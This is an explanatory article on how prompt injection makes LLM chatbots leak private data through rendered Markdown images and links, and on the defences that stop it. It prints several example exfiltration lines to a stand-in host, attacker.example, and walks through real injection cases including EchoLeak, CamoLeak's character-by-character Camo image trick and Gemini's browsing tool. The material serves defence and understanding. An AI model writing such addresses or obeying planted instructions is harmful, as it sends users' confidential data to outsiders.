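# Restricting links and images in the output of LLM applications: what it prevents and what it costs users

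## How can a chatbot's answer leak private data?

An LLM application is a product built around a large language model (LLM), a program that generates text in response to text. The company behind the product adds a chat window to the model, access to the user's mail or files, and often tools for searching the web or sending messages. ChatGPT, Claude and Microsoft 365 Copilot are LLM applications.

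Most chatbots show formatted answers. The model writes Markdown, a plain-text notation that uses punctuation marks to indicate headings, links and images, and the application renders it, or turns it into displayed content. Rendering lets an answer about a holiday include photographs and working links to hotels, but it can also expose private data. A web address can contain text, and whoever runs the server at that address sees the text when a browser requests it. An outsider who can influence what the model writes can therefore try to make it write an address that contains the user's private data.

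Since 2023, product makers have restricted the links and images their applications display. Some remove images entirely, some allow only certain websites, and some ask the user first. These restrictions also block harmless content. Most of what is known about this trade-off comes from security researchers who exploited flaws in the products and from the companies that fixed them.

### What the model reads, and who else can write there

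Before each answer, the application assembles the model's context, a long text containing the maker's standing instructions (the system prompt), the conversation so far, and any emails, files or web pages it has fetched for the task. The context can hold more than users expect. Security researcher Johann Rehberger found stored memories and material from the user's earlier conversations in ChatGPT's system prompt, as he describes in his Embrace The Red post *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*. Microsoft 365 Copilot can draw on the mail and documents that the employee using it has permission to open. Consumers grant AI agents similar access. In Menlo's 2026 report on consumer AI, cited in TechRadar's *This popular AI agent could be hacked by a single email*, 36% had given agents access to their email, 29% to cloud storage and 27% to calendars.

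All of this reaches the model as a single sequence, and the model cannot reliably distinguish the user's request from a sentence in an email that looks like a request. The software developer Simon Willison named the resulting attack "prompt injection", after SQL injection, an older technique in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. At first, people assumed the attacker was the person typing. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) showed that an outsider with no access to the application can plant instructions in material that the application later retrieves, and called this indirect prompt injection. The user is then the victim and usually never sees the instructions.

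Planting instructions for a chatbot takes little skill. Bing Chat could read the open page from a sidebar in Microsoft's Edge browser, and Greshake and colleagues found that text invisible to a human visitor still steered its answers. They wrote that attackers could also plant instructions in email, in public code that programming assistants read, and in text that a user copies from a hostile page into a chat. In *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (2025), Microsoft's security team adds shared documents and tool results to these sources, and notes that a plain text file is enough to carry an attack.

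Criminals have begun hiding instructions for AI assistants in phishing emails, and the security company Barracuda described one such campaign in October 2026. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, the usual hiding places include HTML comments, invisible styling and zero-width characters. Barracuda did not say how widespread the campaign was. The danger it described in that sample was that an assistant would vouch for the email, not that it would leak data.

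### From an email to a server log

Suppose an employee uses an assistant that can read her mailbox. An outsider sends her an email that looks like a newsletter. Below the visible text, the outsider has added instructions for any assistant that processes the email, in white letters on a white background. These direct the assistant to look for mail about a pending deal and end its answer with an image whose address contains a short summary of what it found.

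The next morning she asks the assistant to summarise her mail. The application fetches the new messages, newsletter included, and adds them to the context. The model treats the outsider's text as part of its task. It writes an ordinary summary with one extra line at the end:

    ![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=Offer%20to%20Northgate%3A%204.2%20million)

In Markdown, an exclamation mark followed by square brackets marks an image, and the round brackets hold the address to load it from. Here `attacker.example` stands for a server that the outsider runs. Websites use the part of an address after the question mark for things like search terms and page numbers. Addresses cannot contain plain spaces, so `%20` represents a space, and `%3A` represents a colon. When decoded, the address contains the words "Offer to Northgate: 4.2 million".

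The application converts this line into an HTML image element. Browsers load images as they display a page, so her browser immediately sends a request for the full address to `attacker.example`, and the request carries the data out of the company. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that websites routinely log the addresses visitors request. The outsider can then read the data in the log.

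The request for an image delivers the data, so the server does not have to return a real picture. In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, Roman Samoilenko used a transparent image one pixel wide so that the victim would see almost nothing. Removing everything after the question mark in the web address would not help much because, as Microsoft points out, the data can also be in the path or in the subdomain, the part in front of the domain name.

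How much data an attacker can extract depends partly on the model. Samoilenko found that ChatGPT's randomness sometimes made his instructions fail. It was easy to get the model to copy the user's last message or a piece of code into the address, but very difficult to get it to copy passwords and access keys. In Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, however, Rehberger recorded a demonstration in which a secret from the open web page reached his server inside an encoded summary of the page and the conversation.

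Versions of the leak still turn up in major products. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) describes three ways an email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot send out confidential data, one of which used an image address much like the one above. The main difference was that Microsoft's Bing service, rather than the employee's browser, fetched the address. Microsoft patched that route on 15 November 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot*. The researchers, from the security company Cato Networks, knew of no customers affected by the attacks.

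### The same leak through a link

Without the exclamation mark, the same notation produces a clickable link:

    [Open the full summary](https://attacker.example/s?d=Offer%20to%20Northgate%3A%204.2%20million)

The employee sees only the words "Open the full summary". Her browser requests nothing until she clicks, and then it sends the whole address, including the private text. Samoilenko demonstrated this version too, with code that ChatGPT had just corrected for the user. The attack is less certain because it needs a click, but the link has an advantage over one in a phishing email because it appears in an answer the user asked for. Greshake and colleagues worried early on that people would trust a search chatbot's output more than a stranger's message.

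Researchers classify leaks by what the victim has to do. A one-click leak requires the user to click one link, while in a zero-click leak the final transfer of data needs no action by the user, as when an image loads automatically. A zero-click leak can still depend on something the user did earlier. In the ReLeak cases, the victim did not have to open the hostile email or approve anything, but Copilot had to process that email while handling an ordinary request, such as summarizing her mail.

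An attack can need a click to start but none to send the data out. SC Media's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise* describes one such attack, which the security company Varonis named SearchLeak. The victim clicked a crafted link, which passed the attacker's instructions to Copilot, and an image address then carried the data out with no further click. That automatic transfer is the part that matters for designing controls on output. Messaging apps can also trigger a transfer automatically. Many of them fetch a preview of any link that someone posts, and PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* warns that such a preview can send the data before anyone has clicked.

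### Three conditions, and why makers close the way out

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, reduced these attacks to three conditions:

- the application has access to private data
- it takes in untrusted content, meaning anything an attacker could have written
- it has some way to communicate with the outside

An attacker needs all three. A chatbot that reads hostile web pages but has no data about the user has nothing private to leak. If a chatbot handles only the user's own notes, an outsider has nowhere to insert text. *The Framing Gap* (2026), an experimental paper on agents that use tools, starts from nearly the same list.

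In principle, a maker could remove any one of the three. Removing private data would defeat the purpose of a mail assistant. Removing untrusted content is nearly as hard, since most of what arrives in a mailbox or a web search comes from strangers. In 2025, after researchers showed that a support ticket could make the programming tool Cursor leak access keys, its makers recommended that users connect it only to sources with trusted content. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, thought this advice pretty difficult to follow because attackers have so many ways to get text in front of a model.

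The last of the three conditions for a leak is a way to send the data out, which Willison considers generally the easiest to remove. Removing it takes less away from the product, since an assistant can summarise mail perfectly well without loading images from unknown servers. Willison lists fourteen cases between April 2023 and February 2025, including Google Bard, Amazon Q, Slack and xAI's Grok, and says that vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by restricting the route by which the data left.

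The argument for restricting links and images is strongest for a plain chat window, where they are the obvious ways for data to leak. It weakens as the application gains tools, because restricting rendered links and images doesn't stop leaks through tools. Any tool that can send a web request can carry data out, and so can one that writes to a public code repository. Microsoft even describes a channel in which the attacker learns a single bit from whether the model called a certain tool.

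### Fixed rules and likely defences

Microsoft's security team classes defences as probabilistic or deterministic. A probabilistic defence makes an attack less likely to work but may miss some instances. A deterministic defence guarantees by design that a particular attack cannot succeed, even though the model still behaves unpredictably.

Most defenses against the injection itself make it less likely to succeed but can't rule it out. In Microsoft's Spotlighting technique, for example, the application marks outside text, such as by putting a special character between all the words, and uses the system prompt to instruct the model never to follow instructions in marked text. Microsoft also sells Prompt Shields, a classifier trained on known injections. In the ReLeak attacks, Microsoft's injection protections failed to stop the hostile emails.

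*The Framing Gap* shows how much this kind of protection can depend on wording. In one set of tests, the model leaked the secret 31.9% of the time. The rate fell to zero with a confidentiality policy that forbade disclosure "in any form", but rose to 48.8% with a policy that named specific forbidden behaviours and omitted the catch-all phrase. A developer could not easily have predicted which wording would work. Another probabilistic method, a separate detector that only classified whether a text was an injection, caught every reworded variant without a false alarm. Attacks that succeeded up to 100% of the time against a model through its programming interface failed in all 48 valid trials in the ChatGPT product, for reasons the paper does not establish.

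Willison argues that a detector that catches 99% of attacks still fails by the standards of application security, because attackers look for the 1% it misses. If each hostile email has a 1% chance of getting through, and the attempts are independent, a hundred emails give the attacker about a 63% chance of at least one success. Real attempts are not independent. The chance is lower if the attacker sends a hundred copies of one failed email, since most of them will fail too, and higher if the attacker learns from each failure.

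By contrast, a rule such as "never load an image from an outside server" applies to what the application does with the model's text, so it holds even when an injection has succeeded completely. Microsoft says it designs its systems expecting some injections to get through, and it gives its response to Rehberger's image leak as an example of deterministic blocking. The guarantee covers only the attack the designers had in mind, though, and a rule with a gap will let the same attack through every time. Microsoft therefore uses both classes of defense together, and asks for the user's explicit consent where neither is enough. In Outlook, for example, Copilot can draft an email, but the user has to send it.

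### The first reports and repairs

Samoilenko found the image leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. In his attack, a malicious website hid instructions in text that a visitor copied and then pasted into the chat. Rehberger independently found the same weakness a few days later. He reported it to Microsoft on 8 April and to OpenAI on 9 April.

Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed Bing Chat, and his old tests no longer worked. (His 2026 retrospective, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, puts the fix in May.) As far as he could tell from outside, at least part of the fix was a new Content Security Policy, a set of rules from a website that tells the browser where it may load content from. The policy still allowed images from four Bing addresses, so Bing Chat could keep showing pictures it had made for the user.

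Anthropic fixed Claude differently, by replacing automatic image loading with a "Show Image" button, so a leak now required a click. Rehberger had demonstrated the leak with an uploaded file, a short biography of Albert Einstein with instructions in the middle of a paragraph. He reported it on 12 July, and Anthropic closed the report two weeks later. In Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Rehberger wrote that the fix was imperfect but stopped the automatic transfer.

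The third case was Microsoft's Azure AI Playground, a page where developers try out models. Rehberger rated the flaw only medium in severity, because the playground could not yet fetch outside content and a user had to paste the hostile text in. He reported it on 24 July, and Microsoft finished fixing it on 13 September. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* reports that the fix was apparently one space added between the brackets of the image notation. The application then no longer recognised an image and loaded nothing.

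OpenAI took longer, and first answered that rendering images from Markdown was a feature and that it planned no change, according to Rehberger's post *ChatGPT Plugins*. In December 2023 ChatGPT's web version began to check with an OpenAI server before displaying an image, and OpenAI later rebuilt this check around an index of public addresses. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* notes that the iPhone app lacked the check at first, because the web page itself called OpenAI's server and each app would need its own version. Anthropic may have had a similar problem, since Claude's iOS app appears on Willison's list of affected products for December 2024, seventeen months after Anthropic had closed Rehberger's report.

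## Where can an application check or block what the model writes?

Suppose the employee's assistant writes an answer that contains both an image and a link to the outsider's server:

    You have three new messages about Northgate.

    ![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=Offer%204.2%20million)

    [Open the full summary](https://attacker.example/s?d=Offer%204.2%20million)

When the model writes a link or an image, no data has leaked yet, because several programs handle the text before any outside server receives a request. In a typical web product, the company's server takes the text from the model and sends it to the chat page. A parser works out which characters are formatting, and a renderer turns the result into HTML. The browser then requests any image immediately, but requests a link only if the user clicks it. The product's maker can put a control at each of these steps,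 and later controls can still work if earlier ones fail.

### Instructing the model and checking its answer

The earliest control is an instruction to the model, such as a system prompt that tells it to ignore commands in emails and never to put user data in a web address. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes a version for Gemini in which the application surrounds the content with reminders to stick to the user's task. Microsoft's Spotlighting can put a character between the words of outside text, enclose the text in random markers, or convert all of it to base64, an encoding the model can decode. Microsoft says the three versions differ in how well they work and how much they interfere with the task.

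Defences that rely on the model's behaviour get weaker once attackers adapt to them. SecurityWeek reported that in Google DeepMind's tests on Gemini 2.0, adaptive attacks had a higher success rate against the defences in 16 of 24 cases. Google trained Gemini 2.5 to resist such attacks, but wrote in a later post that indirect prompt injection is not a problem you "solve" before moving on.

An application can also block text while the model is writing it. A model writes one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, and the application picks each token from the model's list of candidates. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study of a leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot, suggests ruling out candidates that would form a web address. The model then can't write an outsider's address even if it follows the outsider's instructions. It also can't write the address of a hotel the user asked about,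 and the developer has to anticipate every way tokens can combine to spell an address.

A classifier can check the model's answer before the user sees it. The classifiers that Google and Microsoft describe look for hostile instructions in incoming emails and files, whereas a classifier for output needs to look for stolen data. Reddy and Gujral's list of warning signs includes passwords, personal details, bursts of random-looking characters (which can mean encoded data) and unusually long answers to short questions. The employee's answer might show none of these. Its addresses contain an English word and a price, so a check for random-looking text would miss them. The same check would block many harmless addresses, because file-sharing services and online shops often put long random codes in their links.

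Chat products usually display an answer while the model is still writing it. If the page loads each image as soon as its address is complete, the request may be sent before a classifier has read the whole answer. The developer can hold back the entire answer until the check is done, which makes the product feel slow, or show the text immediately and hold back only the links and images.

### Parsing the text into a tree

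A sanitiser removes or neutralises unsafe elements before display. The crudest kind searches the raw text for a pattern, such as an exclamation mark followed by square brackets and then an address in round brackets. That would catch the image in the employee's answer. But Markdown has a second notation for images, the reference style, which puts the address elsewhere in the text:

    ![logo][1]

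    [1]: https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=Offer%204.2%20million

The pattern doesn't match here because there are no round brackets, but the browser would still load the same image. The EchoLeak attack exploited this gap in Microsoft 365 Copilot's link filter.

Many Markdown renderers also accept HTML inside the text, so the model can write an image as an HTML element. An address can leave out `https:` and begin with two slashes, and the browser fills in the rest. markstream-vue, an open-source renderer, blocks images with such addresses because they can silently load outside content. A developer can add a pattern for each variant, but an attacker can use any variant the developer missed.

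A parser avoids most of this guesswork. It reads the text according to the rules of Markdown and builds a tree, in which every element of the answer is a labelled node:

    document
      paragraph
        text: "You have three new messages about Northgate."
      paragraph
        image
          description: "logo"
          address: https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=...
      paragraph
        link
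          address: https://attacker.example/s?d=...
          text: "Open the full summary"

The sanitiser then visits every node. It can delete an image node or replace it with the image's description. If a link's address is unacceptable, the sanitiser removes the link but keeps the words. The application builds the page from the edited tree, not the original text.

Some parsers keep reference-style images as a separate kind of node until they convert the tree to HTML. It is therefore safest to edit the HTML tree, where inline and reference-style images have become the same element. Sharing one tree between the sanitiser and the renderer also matters, because if each parses the text separately with different software, an attacker can look for text that the two interpret differently.

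Parsing also reduces false blocks. If a user asks how to insert an image in Markdown, the answer will contain example image notation, which a pattern search would delete. A parser labels the example as code, which the page displays as plain text without loading an image, so the sanitiser can keep it.

According to its documentation, the Markdown renderer Streamdown first adds any embedded HTML to the tree, then removes dangerous elements, and only then checks whether each link begins with a prefix the developer has permitted. It rewrites any other link to point to a default site the developer has chosen. This keeps the data away from the outsider, but a user who clicks may land on a page she didn't expect.

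Even with a tree, the sanitiser has to compare addresses carefully. The documentation of *harden-react-markdown*, an open-source add-on that restricts links and images in this way, points out that an address can contain `/../`, which means "go up one folder". Suppose the developer permits every address that begins with `https://example.com/images/`. The address `https://example.com/images/../go` begins that way, but a browser reads it as `https://example.com/go`, so the sanitiser has to resolve the address as a browser would before comparing it.

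### What the renderer allows by default

The renderer converts the model's Markdown to HTML, and its settings determine which parts become live content. TYPO3's guide for developers adding LLM features to its website software, *Rendering LLM Markdown server-side safely*, calls these settings a security boundary because a model can repeat fragments that an attacker put in its context.

A renderer with safe defaults can still allow leaks. The documentation for markdown-it, a popular open-source renderer, describes its default output as safe without a separate sanitiser. By default, markdown-it rejects addresses that begin with `javascript:` and a few other prefixes, which attackers can use to run their own code in someone else's web page (cross-site scripting). The address in the employee's answer is an ordinary `https` address that runs no code, so those defaults let it through.

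Dify, an open-source platform for building LLM applications, did not restrict images by default when the pseudonymous researcher veganmosfet tested it in December 2025. The test, described in *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, used a chatbot built from a Dify template and two PDF files, one of which contained a hidden instruction. When the user asked about a particular topic, the application fetched the passage containing that instruction. The model then wrote an image address containing the user's name from the chat, and a test server received the name when the image loaded.

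Dify's front end, which runs in the browser, had no Content Security Policy restricting Markdown images, so it could load them from any domain. The demonstration leaked only a name, from a file the researcher had planted, but the front end would also have loaded an image whose address contained a salary or a contract price. A company that installed Dify with those defaults had to add the restriction itself.

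Security specialists disagree about how much a renderer should restrict. veganmosfet would ideally turn off Markdown and HTML rendering in such chatbots. In an October 2025 article, NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks AI applications to find their weaknesses, recommended first restricting image sources and sanitising the output, and disabling all active content only as a last resort.

Google's sanitiser for Gemini doesn't render external images, but it keeps links unless a detector flags them as unsafe. The detector is based on Google Safe Browsing, which identifies dangerous websites, and the sanitiser replaces flagged links with the words "suspicious link removed". This preserves most links, but a reputation check works best on sites that have already attracted attention, and an attacker can register a new domain for each campaign. Google gives no figures for how many bad links the check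 misses or how many good ones it removes.

### The browser's Content Security Policy

A Content Security Policy is a useful second check because it doesn't depend on the application's parser. The website sends the policy to the browser along with the page, and the browser enforces it. A short policy for a chat page might look like this:

    Content-Security-Policy:
      default-src 'self';
      img-src 'self' https://images.example.com

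The first line introduces the policy. The second sets the default for any kind of content without its own rule, and `'self'` means the site that the page came from. The third allows images only from that site or from `images.example.com`, where the company keeps its pictures. A specific rule replaces the default instead of adding to it, so the third line has to repeat `'self'`.

The browser compares the address of the employee's image with the third line, finds no match and blocks the request. She sees a broken image, and the outsider's server receives nothing. This works whether the model wrote the image inline, in reference style or as HTML, because the browser applies the rule to the request.

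Policies are easy to weaken by accident. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, gives an example with a strict default and the image rule `img-src *`. The asterisk permits every server, so data can still leave through images. The draft also includes a warning about policies that restrict images, scripts and fonts but set no default, because they leave other kinds of request open, such as prefetching, in which the browser loads something before the user asks for it. According to CentralCSP's *img-src* documentation, images load from anywhere if a site sets neither an image rule nor a default.

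Browsers also apply the policy to redirects. If `images.example.com` forwards the browser to `attacker.example`, the browser checks the new address and blocks it. After a redirect, however, the browser ignores any folder named in the rule. If a site's policy lists `example.org/path`, an image from elsewhere on `example.org` will therefore load when another permitted server redirects the browser to it. W3C accepted this so that a hostile website could not use its own policy to discover where other sites redirect their visitors.

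W3C recommends CSP as an additional layer of defence behind careful handling of input and output. One reason to keep the sanitiser is that browsers enforce CSP, so it doesn't protect a phone app that displays answers with its own code instead of a browser.

CSP doesn't stop the employee's link. Its rules govern what the page loads, where its forms may send their contents, and which sites may embed it, but no rule in the draft governs where an ordinary link leads. Even with `img-src 'none'`, which blocks every image, she can click "Open the full summary" and send the same data to the same server.

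### Fetching images through a proxy

If a policy permits only a few image servers, a chatbot can't show a photograph from a news site or a shop. An image proxy is one way to keep such pictures. The application rewrites each image address so that the browser asks the company's own server, and that server fetches the picture and passes it on:

    https://images.example.com/fetch?url=https%3A%2F%2Fattacker.example%2Flogo.png%3Fd%3DOffer...

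The new address contains the original one, with its punctuation encoded. The policy can stay strict because the browser loads every picture from `images.example.com`.

When a browser requests an image directly, the server hosting it receives the user's IP address, which reveals her approximate location and often her employer. The browser may also send cookies, small pieces of data that let a website recognise a returning visitor. If the request goes through the proxy instead, the server receives the proxy's IP address and none of the user's cookies.

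But the proxy still has to request the picture from its original address. If it requests the full address, including everything after the question mark, the outsider's log will show the price of the offer beside the proxy's IP address. In EchoLeak, Copilot's policy permitted requests to a Microsoft Teams service, which passed one on in this way. The browser's policy can't prevent this, because a server sends the second request.

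A proxy therefore has to check each address before fetching from it. Reddy and Gujral recommend a signed media proxy. In such a design, the application uses a secret key to attach a signature and an expiry time to each address it approves, and the proxy refuses any address without a valid signature. The model can write something that looks like a proxy address, but it can't produce a valid signature without the key.

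The protection then depends on which addresses the application signs. If the display code signs the address of every image the model writes, the outsider's image gets a valid signature and the data leaves as before. The signature helps if the application signs only addresses it has reason to trust, such as those of pictures the company's own staff uploaded.

A proxy also creates work and new risks. A proxy that fetches any address on request could let an outsider reach machines inside the company's network. Reddy and Gujral advise blocking private network addresses and long chains of redirects, and limiting the size and duration of each download.

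### The click

If the sanitiser leaves a link in place, the application's last chance to check or block it is when the user clicks. NVIDIA's team recommends showing the whole address before connecting to an outside site, or making links inactive so that the user has to copy and paste them. Tenable's *The Trifecta*, a security company's study of Gemini, found that Gemini redirected links through a google.com address, and Embrace The Red describes a similar arrangement in Google Colab that displays a confirmation page. Showing an address or a confirmation page helps only if the user recognises that something is wrong.

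Since August 2026, a website has also been able to have Chrome block the click. Chrome for Developers (2026) announced that Chrome 152 includes Connection Allowlists, a header in which a site lists every address that a page may contact. A chat page could send this one:

    Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://images.example.com/*")

Here `response-origin` means the site the page came from. Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) explains that the browser checks navigations against the list, as well as images and other content. Clicking a link is a navigation, so this header would block the employee's click. Google's Mike West, who edits the specification, argues that separate rules for each type of content are the wrong approach to leaks. He points out in *Connection Allowlists* that data leaked through a font request is just as bad as data leaked through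 an image.

The new header is also stricter than CSP about redirects, blocking them unless the developer opts in. Helme explains in *Connection Allowlist* that this is because the server that receives a request controls where it goes next.

The header doesn't yet solve the problem for every product. The specification isn't a W3C standard, and when Google announced the trial in March 2026, Chromestatus's *Intent to Experiment* (2026) recorded no signal from the developers of the Firefox and Safari browser engines about adopting it. A strict list also suits a general chatbot poorly, because it blocks clicks to hotels and newspapers as well as to the outsider's server. It can also prevent people from signing in, so Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026) warns websites to add any outside sign-in service they use to the list. The header fits best in an internal assistant whose links all lead to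 the company's own documents.

### How the controls line up against EchoLeak

Reddy and Gujral assessed eight controls against six steps of an attack like EchoLeak. In the table below, "blocks" means they expect the control to stop that step, "fails" means they expect at least one way around it, and a dash means the control doesn't apply.

| Control | Model mixes outside text with private data | Email gets past the injection classifier | Link gets past the filter | Image loads automatically | Permitted server passes the request on | Data leaves without a click |
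|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Marking outside text in the prompt | blocks | blocks | – | – | – | fails |
| Using only internal sources by default | blocks | – | blocks | – | – | fails |
| Restricting the output format | blocks | blocks | blocks | fails | – | fails |
| List of allowed or forbidden addresses | – | – | blocks | fails | blocks | blocks |
| Strict CSP | – | – | – | blocks | blocks | blocks |
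| Signed media proxy | – | – | – | blocks | blocks | blocks |
| Human approval for external content | blocks | blocks | blocks | blocks | – | blocks |
| Monitoring outgoing data | – | – | – | – | – | fails |

This is the authors' analysis, not a measurement. They label the table theoretical and state in the limitations section that they ran no experiments and worked only from public information, although one sentence in the paper mentions "our tests". They planned to release an open-source imitation of Copilot for testing such defences.

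Some of the entries are hard to reconcile with how the controls work. The list of addresses is marked as failing against automatic image loading but as blocking the leak without a click, even though that leak depends on automatic loading. Restricting the output format is also marked as failing against images, yet a sanitiser that deletes every image node would stop them, and the paper recommends dropping disallowed images at this stage. Copilot already had a CSP when EchoLeak succeeded. The "blocks" entry for a strict CSP in the fifth column is right only if the policy excludes every server that fetches addresses on request, and the developer may not know which servers do this.

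The table also has no column for leaks that need a click. Strict CSP is marked "blocks" in every applicable column, but it would not have stopped the one-click version of EchoLeak, in which the user clicked a reference-style link that Copilot's filter had missed.

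## What happens when a product removes images or links altogether?

The simplest fixed rule is to show no images, or no links, wherever they lead. A maker who adopts it doesn't need to keep a list of trusted servers or compare addresses carefully. Redirects don't matter either, because the browser never makes the first request. Removing only images still allows data to leak when a user clicks a link. If the employee's assistant removes links as well, she gets plain text, and nothing in the answer can contact a server.

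A product that removes links has to remove the address as well as the formatting. Many chat interfaces turn any text that begins with `https://` into a link, so an address left as plain text may become clickable again. The user could also copy it into a browser. Even complete removal doesn't restrict the application's tools, and the model can still follow an outsider's instructions and write a false summary.

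In 2023, Google removed both links and images from Generative AI Studio, a Google Cloud page for trying out models, after Rehberger showed that an image address could carry the chat history to his server. As far as he could tell, Google fixed this by no longer turning links and images into HTML. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* calls this probably the best possible fix for security. Plain text is a fairly minor inconvenience for a developer testing a model, but it is a bigger problem in an assistant that answers questions about company documents, because employees need to open the documents to check the answers.

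### Amazon Q and links

Amazon faced that problem with Amazon Q for Business, a workplace assistant it released as a preview in late 2023. Rehberger uploaded a text file containing an instruction for the assistant to write a "Sign In" link whose address included a summary of the user's messages. A user might well click it, since people often have to sign in to workplace software again.

Rehberger reported the data exfiltration flaw in Amazon Q for Business on 4 December 2023, and Amazon deployed a fix worldwide on 29 December. According to Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business*, the application then replaced URLs with "[URL not displayed]". In January, Willison (2024) summarised the change as preventing the application from outputting links at all. Microsoft 365 Chat showed users a similar notice at the time that it had removed a URL for privacy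 reasons.

With this rule, an assistant can tell an employee that the travel policy changed, but it can't link to the policy. It also can't link to a supplier's manual or a government form. The placeholder at least shows her that something is missing, so she can search for the page herself.

Amazon Q's citations can also link to files in a company's online storage, according to the AWS guide *Connecting Amazon S3 to Amazon Q Business*. The company can record a web address for each file, and the citation then links to that address. If the company hasn't recorded one, clicking the citation downloads the file.

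These citations are safer than links the model writes because the company sets the address before the conversation begins. An injected instruction might affect which document the assistant cites, but it can't add the employee's messages to a recorded address. This protection works only if outsiders can't edit the records. Citations also cover only documents the company has connected, so they don't replace a link to a manual that is only on the supplier's website.

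It isn't clear whether the 2023 rule still applies to addresses the model writes. Amazon stopped accepting new customers for the product on 31 July 2026 but still provides security updates. AWS's *Amazon Q Business availability change* recommends that existing customers move to Amazon Quick, a newer assistant. Neither AWS page mentions the placeholder.

### Gemini and outside images

Google chose a narrower rule for Gemini, whose sanitiser blocks only external images outright. In June 2025, Google said this rule made the automatic image leak used in EchoLeak "not applicable" to Gemini. It presented the rule as a permanent defence rather than a fix for one flaw, and the announcement carries no later correction.

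The security company Checkmarx also concluded that the rule prevents zero-click leaks through images, though it cited Google's own description as support. It contrasted Gemini with Microsoft Copilot Chat, where Checkmarx's demonstration leaked a secret without a click. According to Checkmarx, Microsoft did not commit to a fix because it did not consider the behaviour a vulnerability. Checkmarx therefore didn't expect Microsoft to fix the version that needs a click either.

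Under Google's rule, Gemini can't load a photograph from a hotel's website or a chart from a newspaper's server into its answer, so the user has to follow a link to see the image. This is a small inconvenience for someone reading about interest rates, but a larger one for someone comparing twenty pairs of shoes.

The rule covers only external addresses, so Google can still display pictures that Gemini generates. These come from Google's own systems, and the application can show them without contacting an outside server. Microsoft made a similar exception for generated pictures in its 2023 fix for Bing Chat. A generated picture works well for a birthday card, but it can't show a shopper what a particular pair of shoes looks like. The application could draw a chart itself from the figures, but the user would then depend on the model to copy the figures correctly.

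Tenable's researchers found that Gemini filtered or restricted images and links, cut suspicious answers short, and sometimes refused to respond. They therefore looked for a way to leak data without displaying anything, and found one in Gemini's browsing tool. An injected instruction made the tool request a URL containing the user's saved information and location, and Gemini didn't ask for confirmation. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* notes that the protections against image leaks did not apply to browsing. Google has since fixed this flaw.

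### CamoLeak and the trusted image server

GitHub, a website where developers store and discuss code, first tried to block only dangerous images in its programming assistant, Copilot Chat. In June 2024 it fixed a flaw that leaked data through images in the version for the code editor VS Code. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes the fix as disabling Markdown images from untrusted domains. On GitHub's website, a strict Content Security Policy also restricted images to domains that GitHub owned.

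In June 2025 the security researcher Omer Mayraz found a way to leak data through one of those domains. Legit Security's *CamoLeak*, his account of the attack, rates its severity 9.6 out of 10. Mayraz first hid instructions in a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code. GitHub lets people hide comments in the description from readers, but Copilot still read them. Copilot also had the same permissions as whoever asked it about the pull request, so it could read that person's private projects.

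Mayraz first got Copilot to write a link containing encoded private text, which leaked if the user clicked. He also wanted a leak that needed no click, but the browser would not load an image from his server. GitHub had a safe way to show outside images in project pages, a signed proxy called Camo, of the kind Reddy and Gujral recommend. When a developer adds an image from another website, GitHub replaces its address with a signed Camo address.

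Copilot could not sign a new address containing private text, so Mayraz collected signed addresses before the attack. Using a GitHub service that converts Markdown, he created a valid Camo address for each letter and symbol and put them all in his hidden comment. He instructed Copilot to spell out private text with the images at these addresses, one for each character.

With placeholder addresses, the text `K7Q` would leak like this:

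    Image in the answer                 Request the outsider receives
    https://images.example.com/sig-K    https://attacker.example/K
    https://images.example.com/sig-7    https://attacker.example/7
    https://images.example.com/sig-Q    https://attacker.example/Q

Every image was a single transparent pixel, as in Samoilenko's attack. Copilot also added a random number to the end of each Camo address. Without that number, the browser could have reused its stored copy of an image when a letter appeared twice, and the second request would never have reached Mayraz's server. Camo accepted the altered addresses, so its signature evidently did not cover the added number.

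In one demonstration, Mayraz extracted the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. In another, Copilot searched the victim's code for "AWS_KEY" and leaked the result.

The signature showed that GitHub had created an address, but not that requesting it was harmless. The private text was encoded in the order of the requests rather than in any single address, so a check that looked at one image at a time would have missed it.

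GitHub told Mayraz on 14 August 2025 that it had fixed the flaw. According to his report, the fix was to disable images in Copilot Chat completely. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* describes the fix more narrowly, saying that GitHub had disallowed using Camo to leak sensitive user information. That could mean GitHub blocked Camo addresses in Copilot's answers but still allowed other images. Mayraz's account is more specific about what changed, but it doesn't establish whether the complete ban is still in force.

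If GitHub had blocked only Camo, it would still have had to check whether any other permitted server could forward requests to an outsider. Turning off all images avoids that work, but a developer who asks Copilot to explain a project can't see the project's screenshots or architecture diagram in the answer. She has to open the project page, where Camo can still display them.

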